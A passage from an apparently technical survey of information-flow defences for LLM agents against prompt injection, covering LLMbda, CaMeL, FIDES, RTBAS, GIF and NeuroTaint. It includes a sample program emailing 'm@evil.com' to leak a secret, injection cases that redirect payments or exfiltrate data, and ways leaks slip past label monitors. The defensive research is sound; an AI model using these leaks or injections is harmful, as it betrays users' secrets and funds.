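`send`, `recv` and `clear` have one more condition. They may run only if $pc \sqsubseteq l_c$, which means that the decision to use the conversation is no more secret or untrusted than the conversation already is. The reason is the gap that Fenton found in monitors that label only the assignments they run. Garby and colleagues show that CaMeL's interpreter has this gap, with a program along these lines:

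```
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

Only the balance is secret. The two possible runs go as follows:

| Step | Balance above the threshold | Balance not above it |
|---|---|---|
| `tmp = False` | runs, so `tmp` is false and secret | skipped, so `tmp` is true and public |
| `rich = False` | skipped, so `rich` is true and public | runs, so `rich` is false and public |
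| Email | sent | not sent |

In the left-hand run, the tracker correctly marks `tmp` as secret. But the program then skips `rich = False`, and because the tracker labels only assignments that run, `rich` stays public. In the right-hand run, `tmp` is still public, so the tracker treats the second branch as harmless. The tracker finds nothing to block in either run, yet the email arrives exactly when the balance is above the threshold.

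Garby and colleagues use Austin and Flanagan's remedy, which is to stop a program that tries to change a public variable inside a secret branch. Here the program would stop at `tmp = False` if the balance were above the threshold. Otherwise it would finish without sending anything, so no email would go out in either case.

LLMbda has no variables that a program can overwrite, so this problem can occur only in the conversation. In the paper's demonstration, a program tells the model to remember that `x` is false. Then, inside a branch that runs only if a secret is true, it tells the model to set `x` to true. After the branch, it asks for the value of `x`. When the secret is true, the interpreter stops the program at the second message.

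Marking the conversation as secret and continuing would protect only the run in which the secret is true. When the secret is false, the program skips the second message, so the conversation stays public and the model's answer reveals the secret.

Stopping the program still reveals one bit, as a policy block does in CaMeL, but LLMbda programs cannot catch a label error and try again.

### Isolation without a fixed architecture

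CaMeL and FIDES build the split between a planner and a quarantined model into their architecture. In LLMbda, a quarantined model is a short function that anyone can write. Slightly simplified, it is:

```
let quarantine = \prompt. fork (let _ = clear in @prompt)
```

The backslash introduces the function's input. Suppose a trusted program calls this function with a prompt that contains an untrusted email. `fork` copies the conversation, and `clear` empties the copy. Sending the prompt then makes the copy untrusted, and the model's reply gets the label U. When the fork ends, the original conversation comes back with its old text and label. The reply keeps the label U, so isolating the email protects the planner without marking the reply as trusted.

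A developer can therefore choose what to isolate. The same program might quarantine an email but let the planner read a list of invoices from the user's own records. The rules also prevent generated code from using `clear` to mark an untrusted conversation as trusted, because `clear` sets the conversation's label to the current $pc$. If the planner has read a forged invoice, its next program runs with the label U, so the conversation stays untrusted even if that program clears it.

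Garby and colleagues demonstrate the difference with an email whose postscript asks for a cancellation note instead of a meeting reminder. A GPT-4o agent that kept everything in one conversation obeyed the postscript. A GPT-5.2 agent wrote its program first, quarantined the email and sent the reminder. The agents used different models, so the results alone don't prove that isolation caused the different outcomes.

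The labels give a stronger reason to rely on the second agent. Its `send_email` function requires a trusted subject and body, so the postscript can't change the wording of any message that passes the check. But the function accepts an untrusted recipient, because the program has to read Bob's address from his email. The theorem doesn't rule out a forged address that redirects the reminder.

### Noninterference when replies are random

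A language model complicates noninterference because it can reply differently to the same prompt. Two runs may differ even though nothing has leaked, so the theorem compares the probabilities of outcomes instead of single runs.

Suppose an observer can see only data with labels up to some level $m$, and two inputs look the same to that observer. For each outcome $q$ that the observer can tell apart from others, let $\mu_0(q)$ and $\mu_1(q)$ be the probabilities that the program finishes with that outcome on the two inputs. For each input, these probabilities may add up to less than 1, and the remainder is the probability that the program doesn't finish because it loops forever, hits an error or fails a label check.

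The strictest requirement would be $\mu_0 = \mu_1$. The theorem proves something weaker, which Garby and colleagues call termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference. For every program and every $m$, there is some $\omega$ such that

$$\mu_0(q) \le \omega(q), \qquad \mu_1(q) \le \omega(q) \quad \text{for all } q, \qquad \sum_q \omega(q) \le 1.$$

In other words, it must be possible to make the two distributions identical just by letting the program finish more often. The smallest candidate for $\omega$ assigns each outcome the larger of its two probabilities, so the condition holds exactly when these larger values add up to at most 1.

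As an illustration, suppose a program answers yes or no, and compare three possible secrets:

| Outcome | Secret A | Secret B | Secret C |
|---|---|---|---|
| Yes | 0.5 | 0.5 | 0.6 |
| No | 0.5 | 0 | 0.4 |
| Doesn't finish | 0 | 0.5 | 0 |

The theorem permits the difference between A and B because the larger values, 0.5 and 0.5, add up to 1. It rules out the difference between A and C because the larger values, 0.6 and 0.5, add up to 1.1. If a program always finishes, its outcomes must have exactly the same probabilities whatever the secret is.

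An LLMbda program can easily behave like A and B. It could ask the model for a random yes or no and, after a "no", enter a branch that sends a message only if the secret is B. The interpreter would stop the program at that message. Garby and colleagues first tried a simpler definition, which required equal probabilities among the runs that finish. This program would fail that definition because every finished run answers yes with B, but only half do with A.

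The same theorem covers integrity when the observer sees only trusted data. In that case, changing an untrusted email can't alter a trusted result, except by preventing the program from finishing, so an attacker may still be able to block a payment.

### How much a stopped program can reveal

The paper also limits how far the finished outcomes can differ. Let $d_0$ and $d_1$ be the probabilities that the program doesn't finish on the two inputs. Then

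$$\frac{1}{2}\sum_q |\mu_0(q) - \mu_1(q)| \;\le\; \frac{d_0 + d_1}{2}.$$

This follows from the existence of $\omega$. For each outcome, the gap between $\mu_0$ and $\mu_1$ is at most the gap between $\omega$ and $\mu_0$ plus the gap between $\omega$ and $\mu_1$. Summed over all outcomes, those two gaps are at most $d_0$ and $d_1$. With secrets A and B, both sides equal 0.25, so the bound can't be tightened in general.

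If a program finishes 99 percent of the time on both inputs, the difference is at most 0.01. If label checks stop it half the time, the bound rises to 0.5. The guarantee is therefore strongest for agents whose policies rarely stop them.

The bound also leaves out anything an observer learns from whether the run finishes. The program that told the model to remember `x` always finishes for one value of the secret and never for the other. The left side of the formula is then 0.5, but an observer who notices whether the program has finished knows the secret for certain.

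This matters more for agents with live tools. LLMbda models tools as functions inside the program, and its theorem concerns the final state. Garby and colleagues list this as a limitation. Real tools can send messages before a program finishes. For example, a program could send an outsider the numbers 0, 1, 2 and so on, comparing each with the user's secret PIN after sending it. If they match, the program enters a branch that breaks a label rule, which stops the run. In LLMbda's model, a stopped run produces no final state, so the observer gets no list of messages. With a real email tool, the last number to arrive would be the PIN. A four-digit PIN would take at most 10,000 messages, and a monitor that checked labels in the same way would flag none of them, because each is a public constant.

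### How the proof works

The proof has to produce an $\omega$ for every program. Garby and colleagues obtain it from a second, imaginary way of running programs. Whenever a label rises above the observer's level, this second way skips the computation and uses an empty value instead.

They then prove three facts. First, the skipping version is at least as likely as the real one to reach each outcome the observer can see, because it avoids hidden computations that might have stopped the program. Second, it gives the same probabilities for both inputs, because it skips everything that depends on the hidden difference. Third, its probabilities add up to at most 1. If $\omega_0$ and $\omega_1$ are its results on the two inputs, then

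$$\mu_0 \le \omega_0 = \omega_1 \ge \mu_1,$$

so their common value is the required $\omega$.

In an earlier proof for a simpler language with random choices, Smith and Alpízar removed the secret parts from the program's text and used what remained. That wouldn't work here, because the model writes some of the text during the run. Skipping the secret parts as the program runs handles new code as it arrives.

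A separate theorem connects the mathematics to the working software by showing that the interpreter that calls the model produces outcomes with the probabilities used in the proof. The theorem assumes that each reply is a fresh random draw that depends only on the conversation so far. A model service that also used a user's earlier conversations would break this assumption, because text could travel through the service without a label.

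The guarantee also depends on developers labeling each source correctly and putting a check in every sensitive tool. If a developer marks a public web page as trusted, the theorem still holds, but it gives no protection against that page.

### Randori and the banking test

To find out whether agents can do useful work under these rules, Garby and colleagues wrote an agent called Randori in LLMbda and tested it on AgentDojo's banking tasks. Randori first practises in a mode where payments do nothing and every file contains the same placeholder text. The model rewrites its program until it runs without an error or the retries run out. The model then writes a final version for the real account, without having seen any of the real data.

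The test combined 16 tasks with nine injections each. Running every combination three times with each of three models gave 1,296 attacked runs. Label checks were on throughout. The same study ran CaMeL with two of the models:

| Agent | Model | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 75.0% | 65.0% |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 75.0% | 63.4% |
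| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 64.6% | 59.5% |
| Randori without endorsement | Qwen3.7-plus | 62.5% | 60.2% |
| Randori without endorsement | MiMo-v2.5 | 54.2% | 56.2% |
| CaMeL, policies off | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 71.1% |
| CaMeL, policies off | MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 72.2% |
| CaMeL, policies on | GPT-5.2 | 37.5% | 30.0% |
| CaMeL, policies on | MiMo-v2.5 | 37.5% | 41.5% |

Without attacks, Randori completed about as many tasks as CaMeL with its policies off, and roughly twice as many as CaMeL with its policies on. These figures have margins of error of around 20 points either way, so small differences in the table mean little.

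The proof doesn't explain Randori's advantage over CaMeL. Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, and enforces those more loosely. For example, its `send_money` requires a trusted recipient but accepts an untrusted amount. Its programs may also use endorsement to mark chosen data as trusted. In runs without attacks, removing endorsement lowered completion by 10 to 12 points. Three of the 16 tasks require the agent to read a file and act on it, which Randori's policies would forbid without endorsement.

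Randori also had disadvantages. CaMeL's planner writes Python, which models write well, while LLMbda is new to them. LLMbda has no built-in error handling, and practice mode doesn't reveal label errors, so the agent may discover one only when it runs the final program.

Attacks succeeded in two of the 1,296 runs. Garby and colleagues divide the 144 combinations of task and injection into two groups to show how much of the resistance came from the labels. In 97 combinations, the attacker needs a tool call or file read that no sensible program for the task would contain, such as a payment when the user only wants a summary of recent transactions. Writing the program before reading the data is generally enough to stop these attacks. In the other 47, the program could plausibly include what the attacker needs, so the labels matter. A perfect score on 47 combinations is limited evidence, and the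 paper's 95 percent interval for such a score goes down to 92.4 percent.

The benchmark doesn't test multi-shot execution. LLMbda's theorem covers an agent that reads real data and then writes more code, but Randori writes its final program before the real data arrives. The banking results therefore don't show how many tasks an agent could complete if its planner read untrusted results and every later program inherited their label.

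### The two successful attacks

Both successes came from GPT-5.2 on the same task and injection. The user asks the agent to read a text file and make the payment it describes. The injection replaces the file's contents with a request to pay the attacker.

Randori labeled the file correctly. But its program, written before it opened the file, endorsed the data it would find there. So when the program ran, the attacker's account number counted as trusted, and `send_money` accepted it.

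The theorem allows this. For programs without endorsement, it protects both secrecy and integrity. For programs with endorsement, Garby and colleagues prove a narrower result called insulated noninterference, which shows that the original guarantee still holds for an observer who looks only at the secrecy part of each label. An endorsement can make an attacker's account number count as trusted, but it can't make a secret balance count as public. The two attacks misdirected money without breaking the secrecy guarantee.

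The result of an endorsement can also never be more trusted than the program-counter label. If a planner reads the file and then writes a program, that program runs as untrusted and its endorsements have no effect. Randori's endorsement worked only because the planner wrote it before reading the file.

The user asked the agent to follow the file, and the attacker controlled its contents. Without endorsement, the check in `send_money` would have blocked the attack, but it would also have blocked the payment if the file had been genuine. Garby and colleagues argue that no system based on provenance can separate these cases, because they differ in the meaning of the text.

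They support this by saying that four independent systems had the same kinds of failure remaining, which slightly overstates the agreement. In CaMeL's original tests, an attack also succeeded on the payment task. The failure that CaMeL shares with FIDES and another system, TACIT, is on a travel task where AgentDojo counts quoting a hotel review word for word as a successful attack. The payment task is evidence of a limit to provenance, but the hotel task mainly reflects how the benchmark scores answers.

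### What FIDES proves instead

Costa and colleagues proved that FIDES satisfies explicit secrecy, a property defined on one path through the agent at a time. Let $g$ be the combined effect of the tool calls on that path. If two sets of stored data, $d_1$ and $d_2$, differ only in their secrets, then $g(d_1)$ and $g(d_2)$ must have the same public contents. The definition doesn't require both sets to lead the agent down the same path. The path that sends the "rich!" email satisfies it because the path's public effect is the same whatever the balance is.

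A single tool call leaks little in this way, but a program can repeat the trick:

```
copy = ""
for bit in secret:
    if bit == "1":
        copy += "1"
    else:
        copy += "0"
```

A tracker that follows only copied data would leave `copy` public because the program builds it from constants, even though `copy` ends up containing the whole secret. The example shows why explicit secrecy would be a weak standard for agents that write code. It isn't an attack on FIDES, whose planner requests tools one at a time and doesn't write loops like this. An LLMbda version would label the result secret because each part comes from a branch that depends on the secret.

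The FIDES proof also assumes a deterministic model, one that always gives the same reply to the same conversation, and it covers one planning loop rather than every program in a language.

LLMbda avoids part of the problem that made Costa and colleagues consider noninterference too restrictive. A program written in advance can store a secret in one variable and then post an unrelated public message, because the two values have separate labels. But their concern is justified for multi-shot agents, because if the planner itself has read the secret, the whole program it writes next is secret and can't post anything publicly.

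### Security relative to an agent that never obeys

Noninterference also rules out disclosures the user wants, so an LLMbda program would need a deliberate exception for them. Dongol's relative security avoids the need for exceptions by comparing the agent with a reference agent that never follows planted instructions.

For each run $t$, the definitions record the secrets it reads, $\mathrm{Sec}(t)$, the untrusted content the attacker supplies, $\mathrm{Act}(t)$, and the messages the attacker receives, $\mathrm{Obs}(t)$. Two runs leak the difference between secrets $\sigma_1$ and $\sigma_2$ if

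$$\mathrm{Sec}(t_1) = \sigma_1,\quad \mathrm{Sec}(t_2) = \sigma_2,\quad \mathrm{Act}(t_1) = \mathrm{Act}(t_2),\quad \mathrm{Obs}(t_1) \ne \mathrm{Obs}(t_2).$$

The real agent is relatively secure if, whenever it leaks the difference between two secrets, the reference agent can leak it too when given the same starting memory and trusted inputs. The attacker may send the reference agent something different, such as an honest meeting request instead of an injection.

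The three standards give different verdicts on Dongol's examples:

| Behaviour after an injection | Noninterference | Explicit secrecy | Relative security |
|---|---|---|---|
| An agent that may share its calendar on request sends the calendar | rejects | rejects | accepts |
| The same agent also sends a password-reset code | rejects | rejects | rejects |
| A quarantined model's answer depends on private notes and decides whether the plan sends a 1 or a 0 | rejects | accepts | rejects |

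The last example is another implicit flow. Each message is a public constant, so it passes a check based only on the message's own label.

Dongol also offers a stricter version that removes the guessing weakness described earlier. It requires a fixed rule that converts the real attacker's input into the reference agent's input without using the secrets. The attacker can no longer choose a different guess for each pair of secrets, and an agent that gives away the whole secret fails the test.

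These definitions can also account for timing, which LLMbda's theorem doesn't. In one example, a user approves the exact text of an email reply, and an injection tries to send some private data. The monitor allows the injected message only if the data matches the approved reply. The attacker receives the same single message either way, but it arrives one step earlier if the data matches. The agent is secure against an attacker who sees only the content and order of messages, but not against one who can also time them.

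Dongol used the definitions to judge 25 small example agents, with about 31,600 lines of machine-checked proof. The definitions require a plan that is fixed before the agent reads untrusted data, since otherwise the reference agent has nothing to run. They therefore don't cover an agent that reads a build log and then writes its own repair. LLMbda's theorem covers that agent, but the whole repair gets the log's untrusted label.

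## Estimating which inputs influenced a model's output

A context label covers everything the planner has read, including text that didn't affect its output. The resulting label creep can block harmless actions. Costa and colleagues note that their framework could instead use a finer estimate of what influenced each response.

Researchers have tried several such estimates, and mistakes in them can have very different consequences. If the system reruns the model without the inputs that seemed irrelevant, a mistake makes the answer worse. If it keeps the original output and only removes labels, a mistake causes label loss, meaning the output loses a label it should have kept.

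### Answering again from fewer documents

*Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models* (Siddiqui, Gaonkar et al., 2024) proposed keeping only the labels of influential inputs. Given a prompt $x$, labelled documents $C$ and the model's answer $y$, the method looks for a smaller set of documents, with a more permissive label, that would have made the same answer nearly as likely.

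In one of their examples, a user wants to know the population of New York City. A search returns a trusted source that gives 8.4 million and an untrusted one that gives about 8 million, and the model answers 8.4 million. To find out whether it needed the untrusted source, the method compares the answer's perplexity with and without that source:

$$\text{perplexity}(y) = \Big(\prod_{i=1}^{|y|} p(y_i \mid x, C, y_{<i})\Big)^{-1/|y|}$$

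Perplexity is 1 divided by the geometric average of the probabilities that the model gives the answer's tokens. Suppose that average is 0.8 with both sources and 0.75 with only the trusted one. Perplexity then rises from 1.25 to 1.33. This increase is within the tolerance of 0.2 that the researchers used in their agent tests, so the untrusted source counts as unnecessary. If the average had fallen to 0.5, perplexity would have risen to 2 and the answer would have stayed untrusted.

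The model then answers again with only the trusted source in its prompt, and the system returns this second answer with a trusted label. If the estimate was wrong, even because an injection misled the search, the second answer may be worse, but none of its text can have come from the untrusted source.

Siddiqui and colleagues tested the method with two sizes of Llama 2. The first test had 64 questions about invented personal records, each with 14 documents that had different labels. The method found the exact combination of labels, out of 16,384 possible combinations, for 86 percent of questions. The introspection baseline, in which the model names the documents it used, was right for 2 percent of questions with the small model and 13 percent with the large one.

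The other two tests used only trusted and untrusted labels. One had 3,465 questions about pairs of news articles, of which 647 allowed a better label than the join. The other had 40 agent conversations, half of which allowed one:

| Test | Method and model | Labels improved, where possible | Improvements that dropped a needed label |
|---|---|---|---|
| News articles | Perplexity, 7B | 57% | 23% |
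| News articles | Perplexity, 70B | 39% | 19% |
| Agent conversations | Perplexity, 7B | 85% | 6% |
| Agent conversations | Perplexity, 70B | 95% | 10% |
| Agent conversations | Introspection, 7B | 45% | 0% |
| Agent conversations | Introspection, 70B | 80% | 11% |

Because the system generates a new answer, the cases in the last column are ones where that answer lacks something it needed. In the agent conversations where the untrusted source was necessary, removing it lowered the answer's overlap with the reference answer by more than 0.3 on a scale from 0 to 1. The problem would be more serious if the system kept the model's first answer, because almost a quarter of the small model's improved labels on news articles would then have been false.

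Siddiqui and colleagues point out that an attacker can still interfere by putting distracting text in an untrusted document. This can stop the system from ever improving the label, which blocks later actions that need trusted data.

The discarded documents also affect which documents remain. Suppose every document has its own label, and the user's records contain a supplier's old and new account numbers. A forged email says the supplier has gone back to the old account, so the model's first answer gives the old number. The search could find that the old record alone explains this answer, and the system would then return the old number as trusted. With only two labels, the system keeps either all the trusted documents or everything, so an attacker couldn't use the email to select one trusted record over another.

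### Hiding parts of the history before each action

In *RTBAS*, Zhong, Chen and colleagues (2025) adapted this idea to agents that call tools. They object that the perplexity search could need 16 to 64 extra model calls with a typical set of four to six security levels. They also object that it labels only a response and has no rule for what happens to the label afterwards. Their system, RTBAS, instead makes one estimate before each step.

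RTBAS divides the conversation into labeled regions, such as a user's message or the body of an email. A dependency screener picks out the regions that matter for the next step. The system joins their labels and hides every region whose label is more restrictive than the joined label. The agent's model then writes its next tool call from the remaining regions. If the tool's policy doesn't accept the joined label, the system asks the user to confirm the call.

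The screener has two versions. In one, a second model reads the conversation and lists the relevant regions. The other uses attention, the weights a transformer gives earlier tokens as it produces a new one. The agent drafts its next step, a small open model computes attention scores for that draft, and a trained classifier uses the scores to decide whether each region is relevant.

Both screeners process untrusted text, so an attacker could try to mislead them with an injection. Suppose an injected email claims to be irrelevant. If the screener marks it as irrelevant and no other untrusted region is relevant, RTBAS hides the email and the agent never reads the injection. If the screener marks the email as relevant, the agent may follow the injection, but the resulting tool call is untrusted and the policy can stop it. Zhong and colleagues therefore argue that screening mistakes can reduce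 performance but can't compromise security.

Better screening doesn't help when the task needs the untrusted text. In one of their examples, a user wants the agent to look up a recipe for lamingtons, a kind of cake, and buy the unusual ingredients. The shopping list has to come from a web page, so a correct estimate still labels the purchase as untrusted.

On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, RTBAS stopped every attack that violated its policy. It didn't track one injection because the text containing it was labelled as the user's own. Without attacks, utility fell by 10 points with the screening model and 7.4 with the attention screener. The drop was largest on Slack tasks, with 22 and 33 percent completed respectively, because many of them involve acting on untrusted web pages. The test skipped suspicious calls, but a real user could confirm those calls and recover some of these tasks. The attention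 classifier's score on AgentDojo may be somewhat inflated because its training data came from 40 AgentDojo cases.

Zhong and colleagues also wrote 37 tasks involving private data, such as booking a flight with a stored credit card. They judged by hand when the agent should ask the user before disclosing something:

| Method | Tasks with an unnecessary request | Tasks with a missing request |
|---|---|---|
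| Hide all private data | 0 | 19 |
| Ask before every tool call | 11 | 0 |
| RTBAS, screening model | 3 | 4 |
| RTBAS, attention | 6 | 4 |

A request can be missing even when no data has leaked. When the system hides all private data, it continues without the card number and the task fails. RTBAS fails similarly when its screener misses private data that the task needs.

The screening model was right 70 percent of the time about exactly which kinds of private data a tool call involved, and the attention screener was right 57.3 percent of the time. Assuming that every call used all the private data was right 56.7 percent of the time, so the attention screener was barely better than making no estimate. On banking tasks, either screener roughly doubled the cost and running time.

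### Measuring influence inside the model

*GIF* (Štorek, Holzer and colleagues, 2026) measures influence more directly. A language model converts each token of its prompt into a list of numbers called an embedding. GIF, short for geometric information flow, slightly changes the embeddings of one passage and measures how much the probabilities of the model's next token change.

In GIF's example, a hiring agent is instructed to require five years' experience with Python and machine learning. An applicant with two years of JavaScript experience plants an instruction in a CV to recommend hiring at $200,000, and the agent follows it. GIF attributes 82 bits of influence on the recommendation to the planted instruction, 27 to the hiring rules and 16 to the remaining text. Unlike a context label, these scores identify the passage responsible. GIF can also score influence on individual output tokens,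 so in a generated program it could trace an account number to one invoice and a file name to another source.

Formally, let $U$ be a small random change to the passage's embeddings and $Y$ the next token. GIF aims to measure the mutual information $I(U;Y)$, which is zero exactly when the token doesn't depend on the change. This is too expensive to compute exactly, so the researchers use

$$\text{GIF} = \tfrac{1}{2}\log\det(I + \tau M), \qquad M = J^\top W^\top F\, W J.$$

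Here $I$ on its own is the identity matrix, and $\tau$ sets the size of the random change. The matrix $J$ describes how the change affects the model's internal state, $W$ converts that state into a score for each possible token, and $F$ describes how those scores affect the probabilities. They prove in Lean that

$$I(U;Y) \le \text{GIF} + o(\tau) \quad \text{as } \tau \to 0,$$

where $o(\tau)$ is an error that shrinks faster than $\tau$. For small enough changes, in other words, the formula doesn't underestimate the flow by any meaningful amount.

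The guarantee covers only small changes to embeddings, whereas an attacker replaces whole sentences. If the model is choosing between two tokens with probabilities $p$ and $1-p$, then $F$ is proportional to $p(1-p)$, which is 0.25 when the model is undecided but about 0.0001 when it is 99.99 percent certain. An injection that leaves the model almost certain of its next token can therefore have a tiny score, even though deleting the injection would change the token. Štorek and colleagues mostly avoid this problem by ranking passages instead of comparing their scores with a fixed threshold, since the model's certainty lowers all the scores together. Ranking doesn't help a system that drops any label whose score is below a set number of bits.

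*Sightline* (2026) studies placeholders, the slots in a prompt that a program fills with values. It proves that, to first order, a value can flow to a transformer's output only through attention that reads it. It also proves that weak attention or low sensitivity is not enough to rule out a flow. In tests on an agent with information-flow control, its method removed about half of the labels from inputs that did not flow.

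This conflicts with one of GIF's claimed advantages. Štorek and colleagues describe an agent that turns private notes into a Reddit comment, which includes a neighbour's name but not the home address. GIF gives the address zero influence, while attention gives it 9 percent. Štorek and colleagues present the zero as a certificate that the address did not flow into the comment. Their theorem supports this only for tiny changes to the address, so a different address could still have produced a different comment.

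### How well the GIF scores find injections

Štorek and colleagues ran six open models on AgentDojo and two other benchmarks. For each run, they took the 50 prompt tokens with the highest scores and counted how many belonged to a known injection or known private data. They then checked whether this count was higher in runs where the agent had broken the policy. A score of 1 means it always was, and 0.5 is no better than guessing:

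| Benchmark | Problem tested | GIF | Attention, as in RTBAS |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | prompt injection | 0.91 | 0.84 |
| MSB | prompt injection | 0.92 | 0.76 |
| AgentDAM | leaks of private data | 0.75 | 0.57 |

These are averages, and attention did better in some cases. With Gemma 4 31B on AgentDojo, for example, attention scored 0.94 and GIF scored 0.80. The test also assumes that the injections and the private data are already labeled, which they wouldn't be in a deployed system.

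In the more realistic version, GIF picks out the most influential passages, and a language model reads them and decides whether to allow the action. With this help, the small model Qwen 3 8B matched GPT-5.5 on AgentDojo and MSB at less than one eightieth of the cost. Because a model still makes the final decision, an injection that manipulates it lets the harmful action run, whereas one that manipulates RTBAS's screening model can at worst produce a badly chosen set of regions.

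GIF can also find attacks that a benchmark misses. In one AgentDojo run, a planted instruction told the agent to send someone's email to an outside address. The agent instead sent details of a calendar event to that address, and AgentDojo counted the attack as failed. GIF traced 31 percent of the influence on the recipient's address to the injection, while attention attributed it mainly to harmless text.

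The calculation requires access to a model's weights, which companies such as OpenAI and Anthropic don't release for their main models. But it can use a different model from the agent's. When Štorek and colleagues used Qwen 3 0.6B to compute the scores for runs by a model 200 times larger, the detection results changed by less than one percentage point.

### Summaries for prompts with fixed slots

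Many programs send a model the same prompt each time and change only the values in a few placeholders. *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* (Xu, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) presents PRISM, a method that analyses such programs in advance and classifies each placeholder by whether its content shows up in the model's output. An ordinary taint tracker can then use the result as it would a description of any other function.

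To develop it, they collected 8,119 pairs of placeholder values and outputs, based on real Python programs. They sorted the pairs into 25 categories, according to how much of the value survived and whether the output was prose, structured data or something executable. A model might copy the value, reword it, summarise it, reduce it to a number (such as a score of 4 for a product review), or ignore it. The tracker drops the label if the category means that none of the value's content reaches the output.

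PRISM achieved an F1 score of 81.7 percent on its taint-analysis test, compared with 62.8 percent for the best baseline and 47.5 percent for tainting every output. F1 combines the share of real flows that a method finds with the share of its reports that are correct. If tainting everything missed no flows, only about 31 percent of its reports were correct. PRISM's F1 score doesn't show how its errors were split between missed flows and false reports, and it could have missed up to 31 percent of real flows.

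PRISM also detected all six known security flaws it was tested on in OpenClaw, a personal AI assistant, and cleared the six repaired versions. In one case, an attacker's message contained a command to print the computer's password file, and the model turned the command into a tool call that the agent ran.

The method is sound only relative to its categories, so a wrongly categorised placeholder can lose a label it needs. Two further limits matter for agents that write code. Xu and colleagues filled the placeholders with plausible values inferred from each program, but a model that ignores an ordinary customer note might still follow instructions injected into one. PRISM also looks for a value's content in the output rather than its wider influence. If a note leads a planner to leave out a safety check, the generated program may contain none of the note's content.

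### Reconstructing flows after a run

An auditor can also investigate after the agent has finished. Cai and colleagues built NeuroTaint for this. It takes a log of the agent's prompts, reasoning, tool calls and memory operations, and reports which untrusted sources influenced which sensitive actions.

NeuroTaint first builds a graph of how data moved between tools, memory and the model. When the agent saves data to memory, NeuroTaint also saves the data's origin, and restores that origin when the agent retrieves the data. This let it connect the confidential revenue forecast to a report that the agent wrote three days later.

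It then examines each sensitive action in two stages. It first compares the action's arguments with earlier sources, using shared words and similarity of meaning. This detects the patient note that an agent had rewritten in an analyst's style. If it finds no match, it removes or replaces a possible source and tests whether the agent would still have taken the action. In the fake compliance procedure example, replacing the poisoned search result with neutral text removes the agent's reason to send the research to an outside address. Each tainted item also has a confidence score between 0 and 1, so the result is an estimate of provenance.

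The replacement test can miss influential sources if they are replaced one at a time. For example, an attacker could plant the same instruction on two web pages. If either page were replaced, the agent would still follow the instruction on the other, so both pages would look harmless.

Cai and colleagues evaluated NeuroTaint on TaintBench, a set of 400 scenarios they wrote based on 20 agent frameworks. NeuroTaint found 93.5 percent of the flows from sources to sensitive actions, and 92.1 percent of the flows it reported were real. Its F1 score was 92.8 percent, compared with 52.2 percent for their FIDES baseline. They designed the scenarios around the three kinds of flow that NeuroTaint detects, so a benchmark by other researchers would be a harder test. In their survey, Wang and colleagues found no benchmark that evaluates the complete chain of provenance.

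The comparison with FIDES also needs care. Cai and colleagues describe their baseline as analyzing known paths between tools, and report that it misses the compliance attack. But the context label in Costa and colleagues' basic planner would mark the call that sent out the research as untrusted, and a policy requiring trusted input would block it. A context label would probably miss fewer flows than the baseline did but raise many more false alarms.

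Because NeuroTaint works from completed logs, it can't stop the run it examines. Its findings can help developers decide which memories to delete and which policies to change. Its threat model excludes attacks hidden in images or disguised with lookalike characters.

*AgentTracer* (Yao, Wu and colleagues, 2026) relies on someone first noticing a suspicious action, then works backwards to the injection that caused it. It groups tool calls by the goal they serve, because an attacker's steps may share no data. For example, an injection might make an agent add the attacker's access key to a GitHub account and later clear its own memory, and the second call has no arguments to trace. In logs that mixed attacks with 9,000 harmless tool calls, AgentTracer identified the injection's entry point 94 percent of the time.

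### Text written to avoid detection

Zhong and colleagues share Microsoft's concern about careless approvals, and add that constant approval requests may lead people to abandon the system. A tracker that uses an imperfect estimate but catches most attacks and rarely interrupts could therefore protect people better than one that catches every attack in theory.

An average miss rate is a poor guide to how often GIF would miss injections from an attacker, who can choose the text. Štorek and colleagues tested GIF against injections from existing benchmarks, whose designers weren't trying to lower a GIF score. An attacker could reword an injection many times, compute the score for each version, and use one that the agent obeys but GIF fails to flag. Small open models work well as stand-ins, which makes GIF cheaper to deploy but also means an attacker could test injections on a similar model on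 their own computer.

Masking is a much stronger defence here. When RTBAS hides an invoice from the planner, the planner can't follow an instruction in it, however carefully the instruction is worded. A note in the hidden invoice also can't make the planner skip a check on the account number. GIF can't score that kind of omission, because it measures influence on tokens that the model wrote.

Masking can't remove an action's dependence on text that the planner needs. In the failed software build, the planner can't find the error without the log, but reading the log makes its repair untrusted. A system that relied only on estimates of influence could, in principle, judge one line of the repair unaffected by the log and label it trusted. This would allow the kind of action that masking forbids, but the label would be only as reliable as the estimate.

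### Small error rates over many calls

An error rate that looks low for one model call can become serious in a long run. Suppose an estimator decides after each call whether to keep a label, every call contains one real flow from untrusted text, and the estimator misses each flow with probability $q$. If the misses are independent, the probability of losing at least one label over $n$ calls is

$$1-(1-q)^n.$$

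| Chance of a miss per call | 10 calls | 50 calls | 100 calls | 500 calls |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0.01% | 0.1% | 0.5% | 1% | 5% |
| 0.1% | 1% | 5% | 10% | 39% |
| 1% | 10% | 39% | 63% | 99% |
| 5% | 40% | 92% | 99% | over 99.9% |

To keep the risk over 100 calls below 1 percent, the estimator would have to miss no more than about one flow in 10,000. None of the published figures above comes close to showing a rate that low, and measuring it would take tens of thousands of test examples. NeuroTaint's miss rate of 6.5 percent doesn't belong in the table because it applies to a whole path from a source to an action, which may include several model calls.

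A lost label doesn't always cause harm. The mislabelled text may never reach a sensitive tool, and most untrusted text doesn't contain an attack. If the original text is still in the prompt at the next call, the tracker may also detect its influence then. But if the planner has summarised an invoice, saved the summary as trusted and deleted the original, every later program that uses the summary will start from the wrong label.

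The independence assumption is also doubtful. An estimator that misses a particular wording once will probably miss it again. In the extreme case, it always misses the same 1 percent of texts and never misses the others. The risk from one randomly chosen text would then stay at 1 percent however many calls the agent made, but an attacker who could find a text in that 1 percent would succeed every time.

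Masking errors also accumulate, but they affect the task instead of the labels. If a screener has a 5 percent chance of hiding something necessary at each step, and the errors are again independent, an agent has only a 36 percent chance of completing 20 steps without such an error. The agent may be able to recover by asking the user or trying another approach.

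## Keeping labels on variables, files and tool results between runs

A context label covers what the planner has read. It doesn't cover data that one program stores and a later program picks up without showing it to the planner. Suppose a user asks an agent to save Harlow Plumbing's invoice, then pay £1,240 to the account number after the words "Pay to:". The agent's first program saves the file:

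```
text = get_invoice(412)
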